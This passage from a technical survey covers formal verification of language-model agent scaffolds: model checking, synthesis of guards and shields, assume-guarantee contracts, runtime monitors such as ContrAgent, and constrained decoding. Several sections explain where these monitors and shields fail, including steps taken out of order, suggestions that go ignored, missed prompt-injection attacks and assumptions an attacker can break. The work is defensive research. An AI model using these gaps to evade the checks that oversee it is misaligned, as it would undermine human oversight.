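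Alternating-time temporal logic (ATL) describes what a group of participants can enforce. The formula ⟨⟨scaffold⟩⟩G(`paid <= 100`) means that the scaffold has a strategy that always keeps the total within the cap, whatever the model does. Garcia de Blas Garcia-Alcalde and Belardinelli (2025), in *ATL*AS*, check such formulas on finite runs by starting with the safe states and repeatedly removing those from which the group cannot be sure of staying within the remaining set. This calculation can also supply the strategy needed to build a scaffold automatically. Jamroga and Murano (2014), in *On Module Checking and Strategies*, prove that ATL cannot express module checking, even in its extended form ATL*. In module checking, the environment can keep several branches open at once, and its cuts are permanent. ATL in its usual form has neither feature. Checking ATL takes polynomial time if the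 input lists all the states, but a program is much shorter than a list of its states. For one compact, program-like input language, ATL checking becomes EXPTIME-complete, as He, Mittelmann and colleagues (2026) point out in *The Complexity of Verifying Strategic Abilities in Succinct Systems*.

### TraceFix

TraceFix, by Xia and colleagues, applies exhaustive search to groups of agents that work at the same time and share resources. Such agents can deadlock, each waiting for another, and this may happen only when events occur in a rare order. A language model, Claude Opus 4.6, first lists the agents, the locks on shared resources and the message channels. It then writes a short program for each agent in PlusCal, a notation that translates into the specification language TLA+. Where an agent must decide something, such as whether to approve a draft or ask for revisions, the program has an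 either/or branch. The model checker TLC explores both branches in combination with every order in which the agents might act. It checks for deadlocks, for two agents holding the same lock, and for locks or messages left over at the end. If TLC finds a fault, the language model receives the failing run and repairs the program.

In one task, in which seven agents write a survey paper, TLC found a deadlock after 97 steps. The data analyst stopped work after serving each researcher once. When the reviewer asked one researcher for revisions, the researcher sent the analyst new data and waited for figures that never came. The reviewer was then waiting for the researcher, and the editor was waiting for the reviewer. In the repaired version, the analyst keeps working until every researcher has finished.

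The benchmark has 48 tasks from 16 scenarios. Thirty passed on the first attempt, including only 4 of the 16 hard ones. The rest needed one to four repairs. The final protocols ranged from 30 states to 7.7 million, and TLC checked each in under a minute.

Seven of the 29 repairs fixed an either/or branch that committed an agent to waiting for one message before it knew which message had arrived. The opponent could then make the agent wait for a message that would never come. Such a branch should depend on which message arrives, because the model doesn't decide that. Another five repairs were needed because TLC ran out of time. Some of these simplified the protocol's branches and retries, which Xia and colleagues acknowledge may leave out behavior the task requires. The searches also limited each channel to three waiting messages by default. Raising the limit to five and seven revealed no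 new faults in four of the five hard tasks with the most channels, while the fifth ran out of time at every setting.

Xia and colleagues then gave each agent its verified program as part of its prompt and ran the agents on simulated tasks. They compared four arrangements, with two models, three levels of injected faults and three repetitions, for 3,456 runs in total. These are the results for the stronger model, gpt-5-mini, with 432 runs per arrangement:

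| Arrangement | Runs that met every objective | Deadlock or livelock |
|---|---|---|
| Protocol in the prompt, with a monitor that rejects undeclared channels, locks and message types | 81.5% | 8.8% |
| Protocol in the prompt, no such monitor | 69.7% | 21.1% |
| A mediator handles all locks and messages | 44.7% | 4.5% |
| Shared chat room only | 29.3% | 32.6% |

In a livelock, agents keep acting but make no progress. The mediator had the fewest deadlocks but completed fewer tasks than the first two arrangements, because it could not adapt when a tool failed. With the weaker model, gpt-5-nano, average task completion fell by about 15 points for the monitor and the mediator, and by 30 to 36 points for the other two.

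This comparison does not isolate the effect of verification, because the arrangements differ in many other ways. A separate experiment isolates that effect, using 270 runs across 15 tasks, all with the monitor. Deadlock or livelock occurred in 31.1% of runs with protocols that had failed TLC's check and 14.1% of runs with verified protocols. Average task completion was 72.6% and 82.1%, respectively.

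TLC had proved the verified protocols free of deadlock, but some failures remained. Xia and colleagues attribute those in the main comparison (8.8%) to agents that took steps in the wrong order. The monitor checks whether an agent may ever use a channel or lock, but not whether it may do so at that point in the protocol. Only the prompt specifies the order, and the model may not follow it, just as it may not follow an instruction never to refund more than 100. In the refund agent, the program fixes the order of steps, so no reply can skip the guard. Xia and colleagues suggest having the monitor track each agent's place in its protocol. That would bring the running system closer to the one TLC checked, but it would not rule out livelock, which TLC did not check for.

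### Agent skills and denied requests

*Methods for Formal Verification of Agent Skills* simplifies replies even further. A skill is a package of instructions and scripts that an agent can load, and its manifest declares the capabilities it needs, such as reading files or using the network. The checker represents each tool request as either a declared capability or the symbol OUT, which stands for everything undeclared. If $D$ is the set of declared capabilities, there are $(|D|+1)^K$ possible sequences of $K$ requests. For every sequence, the checker tests whether the actions carried out match the approved requests in the runtime's log.

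Ten capabilities and eight requests give about 210 million sequences, which is few enough to enumerate. The paper's worked example has three capabilities and 100 requests, which give about $10^{60}$ sequences, too many to enumerate. The paper relies on Z3, a solver that works on formulas and doesn't have to list every case, but the published code contains only the plain enumeration. Neither method is needed if the runtime's decision depends only on the current request. Checking each of the $|D|+1$ symbols once then covers sessions of any length, by the same argument as for a loop invariant.

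The paper's main property, capability containment, has a more serious problem. It requires every capability in a session's trace to be in $D$, the set of capabilities the skill declares, and the trace includes requests that the runtime denied. Suppose a skill declares only file reading, and the model's first reply requests network access. The runtime denies the request, but network access is now in the trace, so containment fails. A model that can output anything can do this to any skill that does not declare every capability. Containment therefore cannot be proved for such a skill unless something prevents the model from producing undeclared requests.

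The paper nevertheless states a theorem that its three checks, together with the runtime's log check, establish containment. The proof starts from an earlier result that no undeclared request reaches the interfaces through which the agent acts on its host machine. It then concludes that the model's part of the trace contains only declared capabilities. This does not follow, because the trace also includes denied requests. The definition should count only requests that the runtime carries out, along with the effects of the skill's scripts. With that change, the argument works if the script analysis is sound and nothing can bypass the runtime's check. Containment would still not establish the refund cap, because it does not limit amounts. If `pay` is a declared capability, an agent with no guard can pay out 5,000 and still satisfy containment.

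## Can a correct scaffold be computed automatically?

A model checker needs a finished scaffold, and if the guard is wrong, a programmer has to fix it and run the checker again. Reactive synthesis starts from the specification alone and either computes a program that satisfies it against every opponent or reports that no such program exists.

Synthesis treats the problem as a game between the model and the scaffold. In each round, the model first returns a reply, which the parser turns into one of finitely many symbols. The scaffold then responds with an action, such as paying, declining or sending a message. A strategy for the scaffold maps the history so far to the next action, so it is a program. A specification is realizable if some strategy satisfies it whatever the model replies.

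Satisfiability is weaker, since it requires only one sequence of replies and actions that meets the specification. Take this rule: "The scaffold pays in this round if and only if the model's next reply is an error." Many runs satisfy it. But the scaffold has to decide before the next reply arrives, so the opponent can wait and then do the opposite. Pnueli (2006), in *Synthesis of Designs from Property Specifications*, gives a specification of this kind and notes that realizing it "requires clairvoyance". The difference is in the quantifiers over replies $r_i$ and actions $a_i$:

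$$\text{satisfiable: } \exists r_1 \exists a_1 \exists r_2 \exists a_2 \ldots\ \varphi \qquad\qquad \text{realizable: } \forall r_1 \exists a_1 \forall r_2 \exists a_2 \ldots\ \varphi$$

Church posed the synthesis problem for circuits in 1957. Rabin solved it in 1969, as did Büchi and Landweber, working separately. Pnueli credits Wolper and Emerson with reviving it for temporal logic around 1981, but says both equated realizability with satisfiability. This assumes that inputs are chosen in the program's favor ("angelic choice"), so the resulting programs work only if the environment cooperates fully.

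In 1989 Pnueli and Rosner solved the adversarial version for specifications in linear temporal logic (LTL), which has operators such as G for "always" and F for "eventually". In the worst case, solving it takes time doubly exponential in the length of the formula. For scale, $2^{2^n}$ is about $10^{308}$ when $n$ is 10. One exponential comes from translating the formula into an automaton, a finite machine that reads a run and accepts it if the formula holds. The automaton may guess what happens later in the run, and the other exponential comes from removing these guesses, which a scaffold can't make.

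### Computing the refund guard

Specifications that contain only safety rules are much cheaper. Let $Force(S)$ be the set of states from which the scaffold can make sure that the next state is in $S$. This means that for every reply, at least one action leads into $S$. Start with the set $W_0$ of states that violate no rule, and compute

$$W_{k+1} = W_k \cap Force(W_k)$$

until nothing changes. This resembles the backward search from a violation, except that the scaffold can now respond to each reply. The states that remain are the safe ones, and in each of them the scaffold may take any action that leads to another safe state.

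Without its guard, the refund agent's scaffold can either pay or decline each request. $W_0$ contains the states with `paid <= 100`. The scaffold can always decline, so no state is removed and the computation stops immediately. Paying `x` leads to a safe state exactly when `paid + x <= 100`, which is the guard derived earlier from the weakest precondition.

The computation is more useful when rules interact. Suppose the shop must also refund 20 for postage if the customer returns the goods. The model reports this with the reply `Postage`, and the scaffold has to pay immediately, though only once per complaint. Now a state with `paid = 90`, postage unpaid and a model call still to come is within the cap but unsafe, because the opponent can reply `Postage`. The first round removes all such states with `paid` above 80, and the second removes nothing. The allowed payments are:

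| Another model call can follow? | Postage already paid? | The scaffold may pay `Refund(x)` if |
|---|---|---|
| Yes | No | `paid + x <= 80` |
| Yes | Yes | `paid + x <= 100` |
| No | Yes or no | `paid + x <= 100` |

The old guard would fail here because `Refund(90)` followed by `Postage` costs 110. A limit of 80 throughout would be safe but would reject some refunds unnecessarily. The guard in the table is the most permissive safe guard, because every scaffold that respects the cap allows only what this guard allows.

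Such a guard can also filter the actions of an unverified controller. In reinforcement learning, where programs learn to act by trial and error, this filter is called a shield. *Explanations for Unrealizability of Infinite-State Safety Shields* (Rodríguez, Shaik and colleagues, 2025) uses shields that correct the controller's action only when it would break a safety rule. A permissive guard makes a good shield because it interferes as rarely as safety allows.

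### When no scaffold can win

A scaffold that never makes an ordinary refund satisfies every rule so far. To exclude it, we return to the agent without postage and add the rule "every request is eventually paid in full". The two rules together are satisfiable, for example by a run in which the model asks for 50 and the scaffold pays. But they are not realizable, because the opponent can reply `Refund(60)` twice, and the scaffold must then either pay 120 or leave a request unpaid forever. A plan that lets the opponent defeat every scaffold is called a counterstrategy.

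This counterstrategy is a fixed list of replies. When we verify a finished scaffold against a safety property, we only need to consider fixed lists, because an opponent that adapts can do no more damage. In synthesis, a single opponent has to defeat every scaffold, so adapting can help. For the rule about paying before an error, no fixed list defeats every scaffold, because for each list some scaffold happens to pay in the right rounds. The opponent has to see whether the scaffold paid before choosing its reply.

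Rodríguez and colleagues call these two kinds of counterstrategy unconditional and conditional, and use them to explain to designers why a shield can't exist. In their example, the environment picks an integer $x$ and the shield responds with an integer $y$. If $x < 2$, the next $y$ must be greater than 1. If $x \geq 2$, the current $y$ must be less than $x$. The explanation is "play 1, then 2", because the second $y$ would have to lie strictly between 1 and 2. Rodríguez and colleagues find such lists by asking a solver whether

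$$\exists x_0, \ldots, x_{k-1}\ \forall y_0, \ldots, y_{k-1}:\ \text{the specification fails within } k \text{ steps},$$

and they increase $k$ until the answer is yes or they reach a limit. For conditional explanations, the quantifiers alternate so that later moves can depend on earlier ones. The search for fixed lists can miss a counterstrategy, but the conditional search finds any that wins within $k$ steps.

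For the shop, the explanation "60, then 60" shows which rules conflict. The designer could promise only that the agent pays each request or passes it to a person, or could assume that the model's requests never add up to more than 100. This assumption makes the specification realizable, but the proof doesn't cover a model that breaks it.

### Recurring assumptions and guarantees

Some guarantees are hopeless without an assumption. Pnueli's example is an arbiter that shares one resource among several clients and must eventually serve each of them. No arbiter can do this if a client may keep the resource forever. Likewise, if the refund agent runs as a permanent service, it cannot keep answering complaints when every reply is an error. We have to assume that usable replies keep arriving:

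$$\text{GF usable} \rightarrow \text{GF answered}.$$

GF means "always eventually", or in other words infinitely often. Bloem, Jobstmann and colleagues (2011), in *Synthesis of Reactive(1) Designs*, study specifications of this form, with any number of assumptions and guarantees:

$$(\text{GF}\,p_1 \wedge \cdots \wedge \text{GF}\,p_m) \rightarrow (\text{GF}\,q_1 \wedge \cdots \wedge \text{GF}\,q_n).$$

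This class is called GR(1), short for generalized reactivity of rank 1. Safety rules such as the cap limit which moves are legal in the game.

With one assumption and one guarantee, the algorithm uses three nested computations. A goal state is one where the guarantee holds, for example because the agent has just answered a complaint.

- The outer computation keeps a set $Z$ of states that may be winning. At first $Z$ contains every state.
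- The middle one grows a set $Y$ outwards from the goal states at which the scaffold can stay in $Z$. It keeps adding states from which the scaffold can force its way into $Y$.
- The inner one also adds states from which the scaffold can wait. While it waits, no usable reply arrives, and the model can end the wait only by moving the game into $Y$ or by breaking the assumption forever.

When $Y$ stops growing, it becomes the new $Z$. This removes goal states from which the scaffold could not return to a goal. The process repeats until $Z$ stops changing. If there are several guarantees, the scaffold pursues them in turn.

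The whole computation takes on the order of $mnN^2$ steps for $N$ states, where each step applies $Force$ to a set. For an agent with 808 states, one assumption and one guarantee, $mnN^2$ is about 650,000. As in model checking, the number of states is the main obstacle. Even so, Bloem and colleagues used the method on an arbiter for a commercial hardware bus, whereas earlier work had covered only toy examples such as traffic lights.

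### Scaffolds that spoil their own assumptions

An implication is true whenever its left side is false, so a scaffold can satisfy a GR(1) specification by making the model break its assumption. Suppose the scaffold can choose what to send, and the game includes the fact that an empty prompt never gets a usable reply. A scaffold that sends empty prompts forever will never receive a usable reply, so the assumption fails and the scaffold satisfies the specification without answering any customer.

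Plain `havoc` does not have this loophole, because it allows a usable reply to any prompt. The loophole appears when a designer makes the environment more realistic by letting replies depend on prompts. A related loophole arises when the environment has no legal input left, since Bloem and colleagues count a run that stops for this reason as won by the system. If the rules allow no reply once a conversation is too long, the scaffold can win by filling the conversation with junk. Allowing an error as a reply in every state prevents this.

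Real tools produce such strategies. *Environmentally-friendly GR(1) Synthesis* (Majumdar, Piterman and Schmuck, 2019) describes a robot in a small maze that has to keep visiting two corners. Another robot can block its way, but the specification assumes that the other robot keeps visiting the remaining two corners. A synthesis tool called slugs found a strategy in which the first robot parks in one of the other robot's corners, or in the passage between them, and stays there. The other robot can then no longer keep visiting both of its corners, so the assumption is false and the first robot satisfies the specification without continuing to visit its own.

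Klein and Pnueli proposed in 2010 that designers check the specification itself. They call an environment well-separated if the system can never force it to break its assumptions. Designers can test this by solving another game, in which the scaffold's only aim is to make the environment break its assumptions. If the scaffold can win from a state reachable in the original game, the specification needs repair, perhaps with a rule that every prompt must contain the complaint.

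Majumdar and colleagues instead change what counts as a solution. After every finite run, the environment must still be able to continue in a way that meets its assumptions, which rules out the scaffold that sends empty prompts. This requirement is about what remains possible, like "tea always remains possible" in module checking, so no extra linear-time clause can express it. The new algorithm adds a fourth nested computation to check that waiting states still have a path forward, and the computation it needs still grows with $N^2$. In the maze, the two robots now take turns in the passage. But for a language model, "possible" may be a weak requirement. If the game counts a badly confusing prompt as answerable, a scaffold that sends nothing else can still pass.

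### Shields for language-model agents

No published work seems to synthesise a scaffold with the language model as the opponent. The closest is the shield in *MENTOR* (Anand, Chatzi and colleagues, 2026), which uses a synthesis game where the model is the agent choosing tool calls and the opponent chooses what the tools return.

The shield is built from a written manual. A travel manual might require the agent to check the distance before booking, forbid flights under 500 km and require that a booking eventually succeed. Claude Opus 5 translates the manual into LTL formulas and constraints on tool-call arguments. A program turns the formulas into a game and marks each call in each state as unsafe, progressing or neither. At run time, the shield blocks unsafe calls and suggests one that would make progress.

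The suggestions matter because blocking alone can leave an agent stuck. In one task, the agent was not entitled to book business class. An earlier rule-based guard blocked that booking in 13 of 20 runs, but in 5 of those 13 the agent never booked any flight. Across four sets of tasks, the new shield raised the share of tasks completed correctly in all five attempts. The gain was 14 to 27 percentage points for GPT-5.4 mini and 3 to 14 points for Claude Haiku 4.5.

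With an arbitrary model, the shield can still block unsafe calls if the rules were translated correctly and a second language model has correctly read any free text from the tools. Anand and colleagues acknowledge that they cannot guarantee a correct translation. The shield also cannot ensure that the agent completes the task, because the agent may ignore every suggestion and keep making harmless calls. In the tests on those four sets, the shield let the agent stop after 25 tool calls even if it had not finished its duties.

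### What the tools can handle

Tools for full LTL do much better than the worst case suggests. *SemML 2.0* (Křetínský, Meggendorfer and Prokop, 2026) reports tests of one such tool on 1,585 specifications from the field's annual competition, with 30 minutes for each. The tool decided realizability for 1,412 and produced circuits for 1,375. Many of these problems are easy, since all four tools in the comparison solved 924 of them in under ten seconds. None solved the hardest 128. The tool avoids building the whole automaton and uses machine learning to guess which parts matter. For an unrealizable specification, it can output the environment's counterstrategy as a program.

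These tools work with true-or-false variables, so amounts of money need an extra step. Rodríguez and colleagues replace each numerical condition with a true-or-false variable and add a formula that records which combinations of values each player can bring about. This method works for some fragments of LTL with numbers.

Language models can also do the synthesis. In *Natural Synthesis* (2026), a model reads the specification and writes either a circuit or a counterstrategy, and a model checker tests the result. If the check fails, the model gets the failing run and tries again. With at most two retries, GPT-5.5 solved 1,467 of 1,586 competition problems, while the winner of the 2025 competition solved 1,297. Newer results from Křetínský and colleagues narrow the gap to about 90 problems, although the time limits differed. The model checker accepts only correct solutions, so a wrong attempt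 only wastes time. A developer could have a model write a scaffold in the same way and rely on the checker's proof instead of trusting the model.

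## What may be assumed about the model, and how do assumptions enter a proof?

An arbitrary model can send gibberish forever, so we cannot prove that the refund agent ever answers a customer, even though it usually would with a real model. Giannakopoulou, Păsăreanu and Barringer (2002), in *Assumption Generation for Software Component Verification*, call checking a component against every possible environment "overly pessimistic", because the component only has to work in the environments where it will be used. The usual remedy is to add an assumption about the environment to the claim and keep track of who has to make it true.

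### Contracts

A contract is a pair $(A, G)$ of sets of behaviors. The assumption $A$ contains the behaviors in which the environment does its part, and the guarantee $G$ those in which the component does its part. In the definition that Xiao, Liu and Nuzzo (2026), in *Symbolic Temporal Supervision of LLM Agents Using Contracts*, apply to agents, a component with behaviors $M$ satisfies the contract if

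$$M \subseteq G \cup \overline{A},$$

where $\overline{A}$ is everything outside $A$. Every behavior must therefore either meet the guarantee or break the assumption. Suppose $A$ is "the requested refunds add up to at most 100" and $G$ is "the payments add up to at most 100". A refund agent with no guard satisfies this contract, because it pays exactly what the model requests.

An assumption does not constrain the environment. Abadi and Lamport (1993), in *Composing Specifications*, give the example of a keyboard. Its specification may assume that nobody presses two keys at once, but the keyboard cannot control anyone's fingers. Something else has to make the assumption true, and the basic composition rule has a separate premise for this. Write $\langle A, S, P \rangle$ for "any system that contains $S$ and satisfies $A$ also satisfies $P$". For a scaffold $S$ and a model $M$, the rule is

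$$\frac{\langle A, S, P \rangle \qquad \langle \text{true}, M, A \rangle}{\langle \text{true}, S \parallel M, P \rangle}$$

where $S \parallel M$ means the two running together. The scaffold's programmer can prove the first premise. The second is a claim about the model, and proving it meets all the obstacles to verifying the model itself. If $A$ is "true", the second premise is trivial and the rule reduces to a proof against an arbitrary model.

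### Components that rely on each other

In a system with several components, one component's guarantee can serve as another's assumption. Misra and Chandy gave a proof rule of this kind for processes that exchange messages, and Jones gave one in 1983 for programs that share variables. Abadi and Lamport then worked out when circular reasoning of this kind is valid.

*Conjoining Specifications* (1995) gives an example with two variables, `c` and `d`, both initially 0. One process repeatedly runs `c := d` and the other repeatedly runs `d := c`. The first guarantees that `c` stays 0 if `d` does, and the second guarantees that `d` stays 0 if `c` does. Concluding from these guarantees that both variables stay 0 is circular, but the conclusion is correct. For it to fail, one process would have to be the first to change its variable, but its assumption would still be true at that moment, so its guarantee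 rules out the change.

This is an induction on steps. Each process's guarantee holds in the starting state. If a process's assumption has held up to step $n$, its guarantee holds up to step $n+1$. So if both guarantees hold up to step $n$, both hold up to step $n+1$.

If we replace "stays 0" with "eventually becomes 1", each process still meets its contract, since it would copy a 1 if the other variable ever became 1. But together they leave both variables at 0 forever. The induction fails because neither process breaks its guarantee at any particular step.

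Agents can deadlock in the same way. Suppose the refund agent pays once a warehouse agent confirms the return, and the warehouse agent confirms the return once it sees the payment. Each eventually acts if the other does, but neither acts first, so both wait forever.

Even for safety, a contract written as "if $A$ then $G$" is too weak, because it would allow the refund agent to overpay on the first call as long as the model breaks the assumption on the third. Abadi and Lamport first used this form, then replaced it with a stronger one in which the guarantee must stay true at least one step longer than the assumption, so the refund agent may overpay only after the model has broken the assumption.

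Their 1993 theorem allows guarantees to include liveness, but the assumptions must be safety properties. "Usable replies keep arriving" is a liveness assumption, so we cannot use the theorem to derive it from a scaffold that itself depends on usable replies. Some circular rules handle liveness soundly, but *On the Completeness of Compositional Reasoning* shows that several of them cannot prove every true statement, and the statements they cannot prove are typically liveness properties.

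### The weakest assumption

A programmer can find an assumption by trial and error, ruling out one unrealistic counterexample after another. Giannakopoulou and colleagues automated the search for safety properties. Their algorithm reports that the component satisfies the property in every environment, that it satisfies it in none, or that it satisfies it exactly in the environments that meet a certain assumption. This is the weakest assumption $A_w$, and they prove that for every environment $E$,

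$$E \text{ satisfies } A_w \iff E \parallel S \text{ satisfies } P.$$

We can calculate the weakest assumption by hand for the faulty guard `if x <= 100`. The earlier proof of the cap failed because it needed a condition that does not hold for every reply. We now require that condition only of the replies the model sends. If a requested amount is at most 100, it must also be at most $100 - paid$. Larger requests need no restriction because the guard already blocks them. This assumption excludes all the replies that would break the cap and no others, so no weaker assumption would suffice. The programmer forgot to check that the amount is at most $100 - paid$, and adding that check to the scaffold reduces the assumption to "true".

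To find the assumption, the algorithm combines the component with a monitor that enters an error state when the property fails, and hides the component's internal steps. It then marks every state from which internal steps alone can lead to the error, since no environment could prevent that. Next, it makes the result deterministic and treats any sequence of inputs that might lead to an error as an error. Inputs to which the component never reacts remain unrestricted. Deleting the error state leaves the assumption. This resembles a synthesis game with the sides exchanged, where the component plays to reach the error state and the environment plays to avoid it.

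If the shop refunds only 50 or 100 at a time, and we ignore the limit on calls, the assumption has three states. Before any refund is paid, the model may request either amount. After a refund of 50, it may request only another 50, and after 100 in total, it may request nothing more. An assumption can also show that the component is badly broken. If an agent pays 150 for any refund request, the weakest assumption is that the model never requests a refund.

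Giannakopoulou and colleagues tested the method on control software for an experimental Mars rover. A developer suspected that two modules could interfere through a shared variable, but could not produce a run that showed it. The generated assumption had seven states and required one module to hold a lock from reading the variable until clearing it. That module's design met the requirement, so the suspected interference could not occur in the design.

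### Neural networks that steer aircraft

In *Assumption Generation for the Verification of Learning-Enabled Autonomous Systems* (2023), Păsăreanu, Mangal and colleagues applied the method to a system that keeps an airplane near the centre line of a taxiway. A 24-layer neural network called TaxiNet estimates the plane's heading and its distance from the line from camera images, and a conventional controller then steers. The plane must stay within 8 metres of the line and turn no more than 35 degrees from it. Păsăreanu and colleagues let the network's estimates take any value and computed the conditions those estimates would have to satisfy to keep the plane within these limits.

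With nine possible estimates, the controller and the airplane's motion together had 99 states, and the assumption had seven. With 303 possible estimates, they had 92,709 states, the assumption had 301, and the computation took 82 seconds. The assumption allows some wrong estimates. For example, three of the nine estimates make the controller steer straight ahead, so the network may output one in place of another without endangering a plane that is already on course.

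The system cannot check an assumption that mentions the plane's true position, because it relies on the network to estimate that position. Păsăreanu and colleagues therefore also generated a stricter assumption about the estimates alone, and used a monitor to stop the system when the estimates violate it. Under their model of the controller and the plane, the monitored system is safe whatever the network outputs. But using error rates from 11,108 images, they calculated that the probability of a stop tends to 1 as runs get longer. With a more accurate network, that probability rises more slowly but still tends to 1.

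### What supports an assumption

An assumption has the strongest support when the system is built to make violations impossible. The refund agent's parser rejects negative amounts, so the rest of the program can assume that `x` is at least 0. Constrained decoding, which masks tokens during generation, can likewise guarantee the format of a reply.

A program can also check an assumption at run time, by testing each reply and using a fallback if the test fails. The code that runs after a successful test may assume the condition holds. This works for "the amount is at most 100 minus `paid`", because the scaffold has access to both numbers. It does not work for "the complaint is genuine", which depends on facts the scaffold does not have access to, or for "a usable reply eventually arrives", because waiting for any finite time cannot show that to be false.

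Other assumptions are supported only by tests. In Shashank's trials with Claude models, for example, the guard had nothing to block in 82 turns. Even if those turns were independent samples, the true violation rate could be as high as 3.6% of turns, at 95% confidence. An attacker may also choose inputs that the tests did not include.

A false assumption does not make the contract false. Suppose the agent has no guard and the contract assumes that requests add up to at most 100. If the model returns `Refund(5000)`, the agent pays 5,000. This run lies in $\overline{A}$, so the agent still satisfies $M \subseteq G \cup \overline{A}$ and the proof is still correct, but the contract does not protect the shop. Tools can rule out impossible assumptions by checking that $A$ is not empty, but that check does not catch an assumption like this one, which is possible but false. A proof that relies on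 an assumption should therefore state what supports that assumption.

### ContrAgent

ContrAgent, built by Xiao and colleagues, checks contracts at run time. It records an agent's tool calls in order and runs simple tests on each one, such as whether the agent is calling the refund tool or whether the amount is within a limit. Formulas in a temporal logic for finite runs combine these tests into contracts, and ContrAgent tracks each formula as a small state machine. In one example, the agent needs approval before it makes a refund, and the limit is $42. If the agent proposes a $50 refund after approval, ContrAgent blocks the call before the tool runs.

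ContrAgent treats the whole agent, including its model, as the component, and users, tools and other agents as the environment. In a proof about the scaffold, ContrAgent's guarantees become assumptions about the model, and a monitor enforces them.

ContrAgent tracks the contract's assumption separately. If the environment permanently violates the assumption, the contract becomes idle and the agent can no longer fail it. So when the system scores recorded runs, it doesn't penalize the agent for anything it does under a violated assumption. During live runs, the system can withhold a tool result that violates an assumption, but it can't undo what the tool has already done.

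Xiao and colleagues tested live enforcement on SOPBench, a set of customer-service tasks with explicit procedures. Some tasks were allowed and others were forbidden. These are the averages over seven domains with Gemini 2.5 Flash:

| Arrangement | Allowed tasks completed | Forbidden tasks blocked | Extra time per task |
|---|---|---|---|
| No procedure given | 91% | 32% | none |
| Procedure in the prompt | 64% | 94% | 0.9 s |
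| Second model judges each call | 24% | 98% | 1.3 s |
| ContrAgent | 90% | 98% | 0.1 s |

With a weaker model, the prompt blocked only 45% of forbidden tasks, while ContrAgent still blocked 98%. ContrAgent's completion rate fell from 90% to 68%, because a monitor cannot make up for a model's lack of ability. The benchmark supplies its procedures in structured form, so this test provides little evidence of how well rules can be translated from ordinary prose. ContrAgent's contracts caught about 75% of 5,435 recorded unsafe runs from the same benchmark and missed the rest mostly because no contract covered them.

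ContrAgent reduced the success rate of recorded prompt-injection attacks against 22 models from 18.0% to 5.3%. In 82% of the attacks it missed, the agent made no malicious tool call, so the monitor had nothing to block. Xiao and colleagues also report a rate of 1.7% with learned contracts, but they tested those contracts on the same attacks they had learned them from.

Another of their tests shows the risk of assuming that a model follows its written policy. On customer-service tasks in three domains, Claude 3.7 reached the correct final state in all four attempts on 25–60% of tasks, but it never did so without breaking a rule. Most violations were of a rule against writing to the user and calling a tool in the same turn. Leaving out that rule raised the rate of fully compliant success to 19–59%.

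### Should contracts be probabilistic?

Bensalem, Dong and colleagues (2026), in *A Three-Layer Probabilistic Assume-Guarantee Architecture Is Structurally Required*, argue that safe deployment needs contracts that hold with a stated probability. Their example is a care robot with three layers of checks. The user layer compares the plan with policy, the operational layer checks that conditions are ones the robot is certified for, and the functional layer controls its movements. Each layer's guarantee supplies the next layer's assumption, so the probability that all three hold is

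$$P(\text{safe}) = p_U \cdot p_{O|U} \cdot p_{F|OU},$$

where $p_{O|U}$ is the probability that the operational layer works given that the user layer did, and $p_{F|OU}$ is defined similarly. With illustrative values of 0.95, 0.94 and 0.96, the result is 0.857.

They accept that yes-or-no guarantees are better where possible, but give two reasons why a whole system cannot have them. The first is that a language model's randomness makes such a guarantee "ill-defined". The refund cap is a counterexample, because it has an exact meaning and a proof that holds no matter how the model produces its replies.

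Their other reason is that sensors are noisy and the world is only partly observable. This reason is stronger, because no controller can avoid a person if its sensor readings can be anything and it has to keep moving. But the TaxiNet monitor can stop the plane, so it gives a yes-or-no guarantee for arbitrary estimates, provided that the model of the plane's motion is right and stopping is safe. Probabilities are still needed to describe how often the plane finishes its journey, or how often a refund goes to someone who deserves it.

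The probabilities are also hard to obtain. Bensalem and colleagues acknowledge that the steps of an agent's run are not independent, that one model behind several layers can make them fail together, and that a new model needs new estimates. An attacker can change the probabilities too. Bensalem and colleagues cite tests in which language models failed to recognise 12% of requests outside their domain, and 71% when the requests were disguised.

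They also mistake an upper bound for a lower bound. Their formula takes a simpler lower bound and adds the probabilities that each pair of layers fails together, which makes the result too high by the probability that all three layers fail at once. In their example, the formula gives 0.830, while the exact calculation from the same figures gives 0.826.

A worst-case proof can still be combined with a measured probability. If every run of the scaffold that satisfies $A$ also satisfies $G$, then

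$$P(G) \geq P(A)$$

for every distribution of replies. Suppose that the model's requests satisfy the weakest assumption for the faulty guard in 99.9% of complaints. Then the agent respects the cap in at least 99.9% of complaints, and the only uncertainty is in the measurement. With the correct guard, $A$ is "true" and the bound is 100%. The 99.9% applies only to customers like those in the sample, and may be far too high for customers who know about the faulty guard.

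## What does constrained decoding guarantee about the output?

Constrained decoding enforces an assumption about a reply's format while the model is still writing, by restricting which token may come next. It keeps the model from producing broken JSON, which the refund agent's parser rejects only after it arrives.

### Masking one token at a time

Before the decoding program draws each token, a checker compares the text so far with a grammar and masks every token that would make a grammatical result impossible. The program sets the probabilities of masked tokens to zero and scales up the rest to add up to 1, without changing the model's weights.

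Suppose the model is writing a sum and has produced `1`. It gives `)` a probability of 50%, `+` 30% and the end marker 20%. There is no open parenthesis to close, so the checker masks `)`. The program then draws `+` with probability 60% or ends with probability 40%.

Bhat, Dandu and colleagues (2027), in *Machine-Checked Grammar-Constrained Decoding*, define exactly what the checker has to decide. Let $V$ be the vocabulary, $L$ the set of grammatical strings, and $\text{detok}(w)$ the text that a token sequence $w$ spells. A prefix $w$ is viable if some continuation makes it grammatical:

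$$\exists u \in V^*:\ \text{detok}(wu) \in L.$$

A mask is sound if every token it allows after a viable prefix produces another viable prefix. It is complete if it allows every token that produces one. The mask may allow the end marker only when the text is already in $L$.

Their example grammar describes sums of numbers with parentheses, such as `(1+2)+1`. Some tokens contain more than one character:

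| Text so far | `+` | `)` | `1` | `)+` | End |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| `1` | allowed | masked | allowed | masked | allowed |
| `(1` | allowed | allowed | allowed | allowed | masked |
| `1+` | masked | masked | allowed | masked | masked |

If the mask is sound, every finished output is grammatical, because the mask allows the end marker only when the text so far is in $L$. Every prefix the decoder produces is also viable, since the empty text is viable as long as $L$ is not empty and each allowed token preserves viability. If the mask is also complete, the decoder never gets stuck, because a viable prefix is either in $L$, so the mask allows the end marker, or has a continuation whose first token the mask allows.

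A safety proof about a scaffold requires only that the mask be sound, meaning that it blocks every string the proof doesn't cover. The mask may also block valid replies, because removing replies cannot break a safety property.

This test suits models that generate text from left to right. Diffusion language models can fill in tokens in any order, so *Constrained Decoding of Diffusion LLMs with Context-Free Grammars* (Mündler, Dekoninck and Vechev, 2025) instead tests whether the remaining gaps can be filled.

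### Why fast checkers have been wrong

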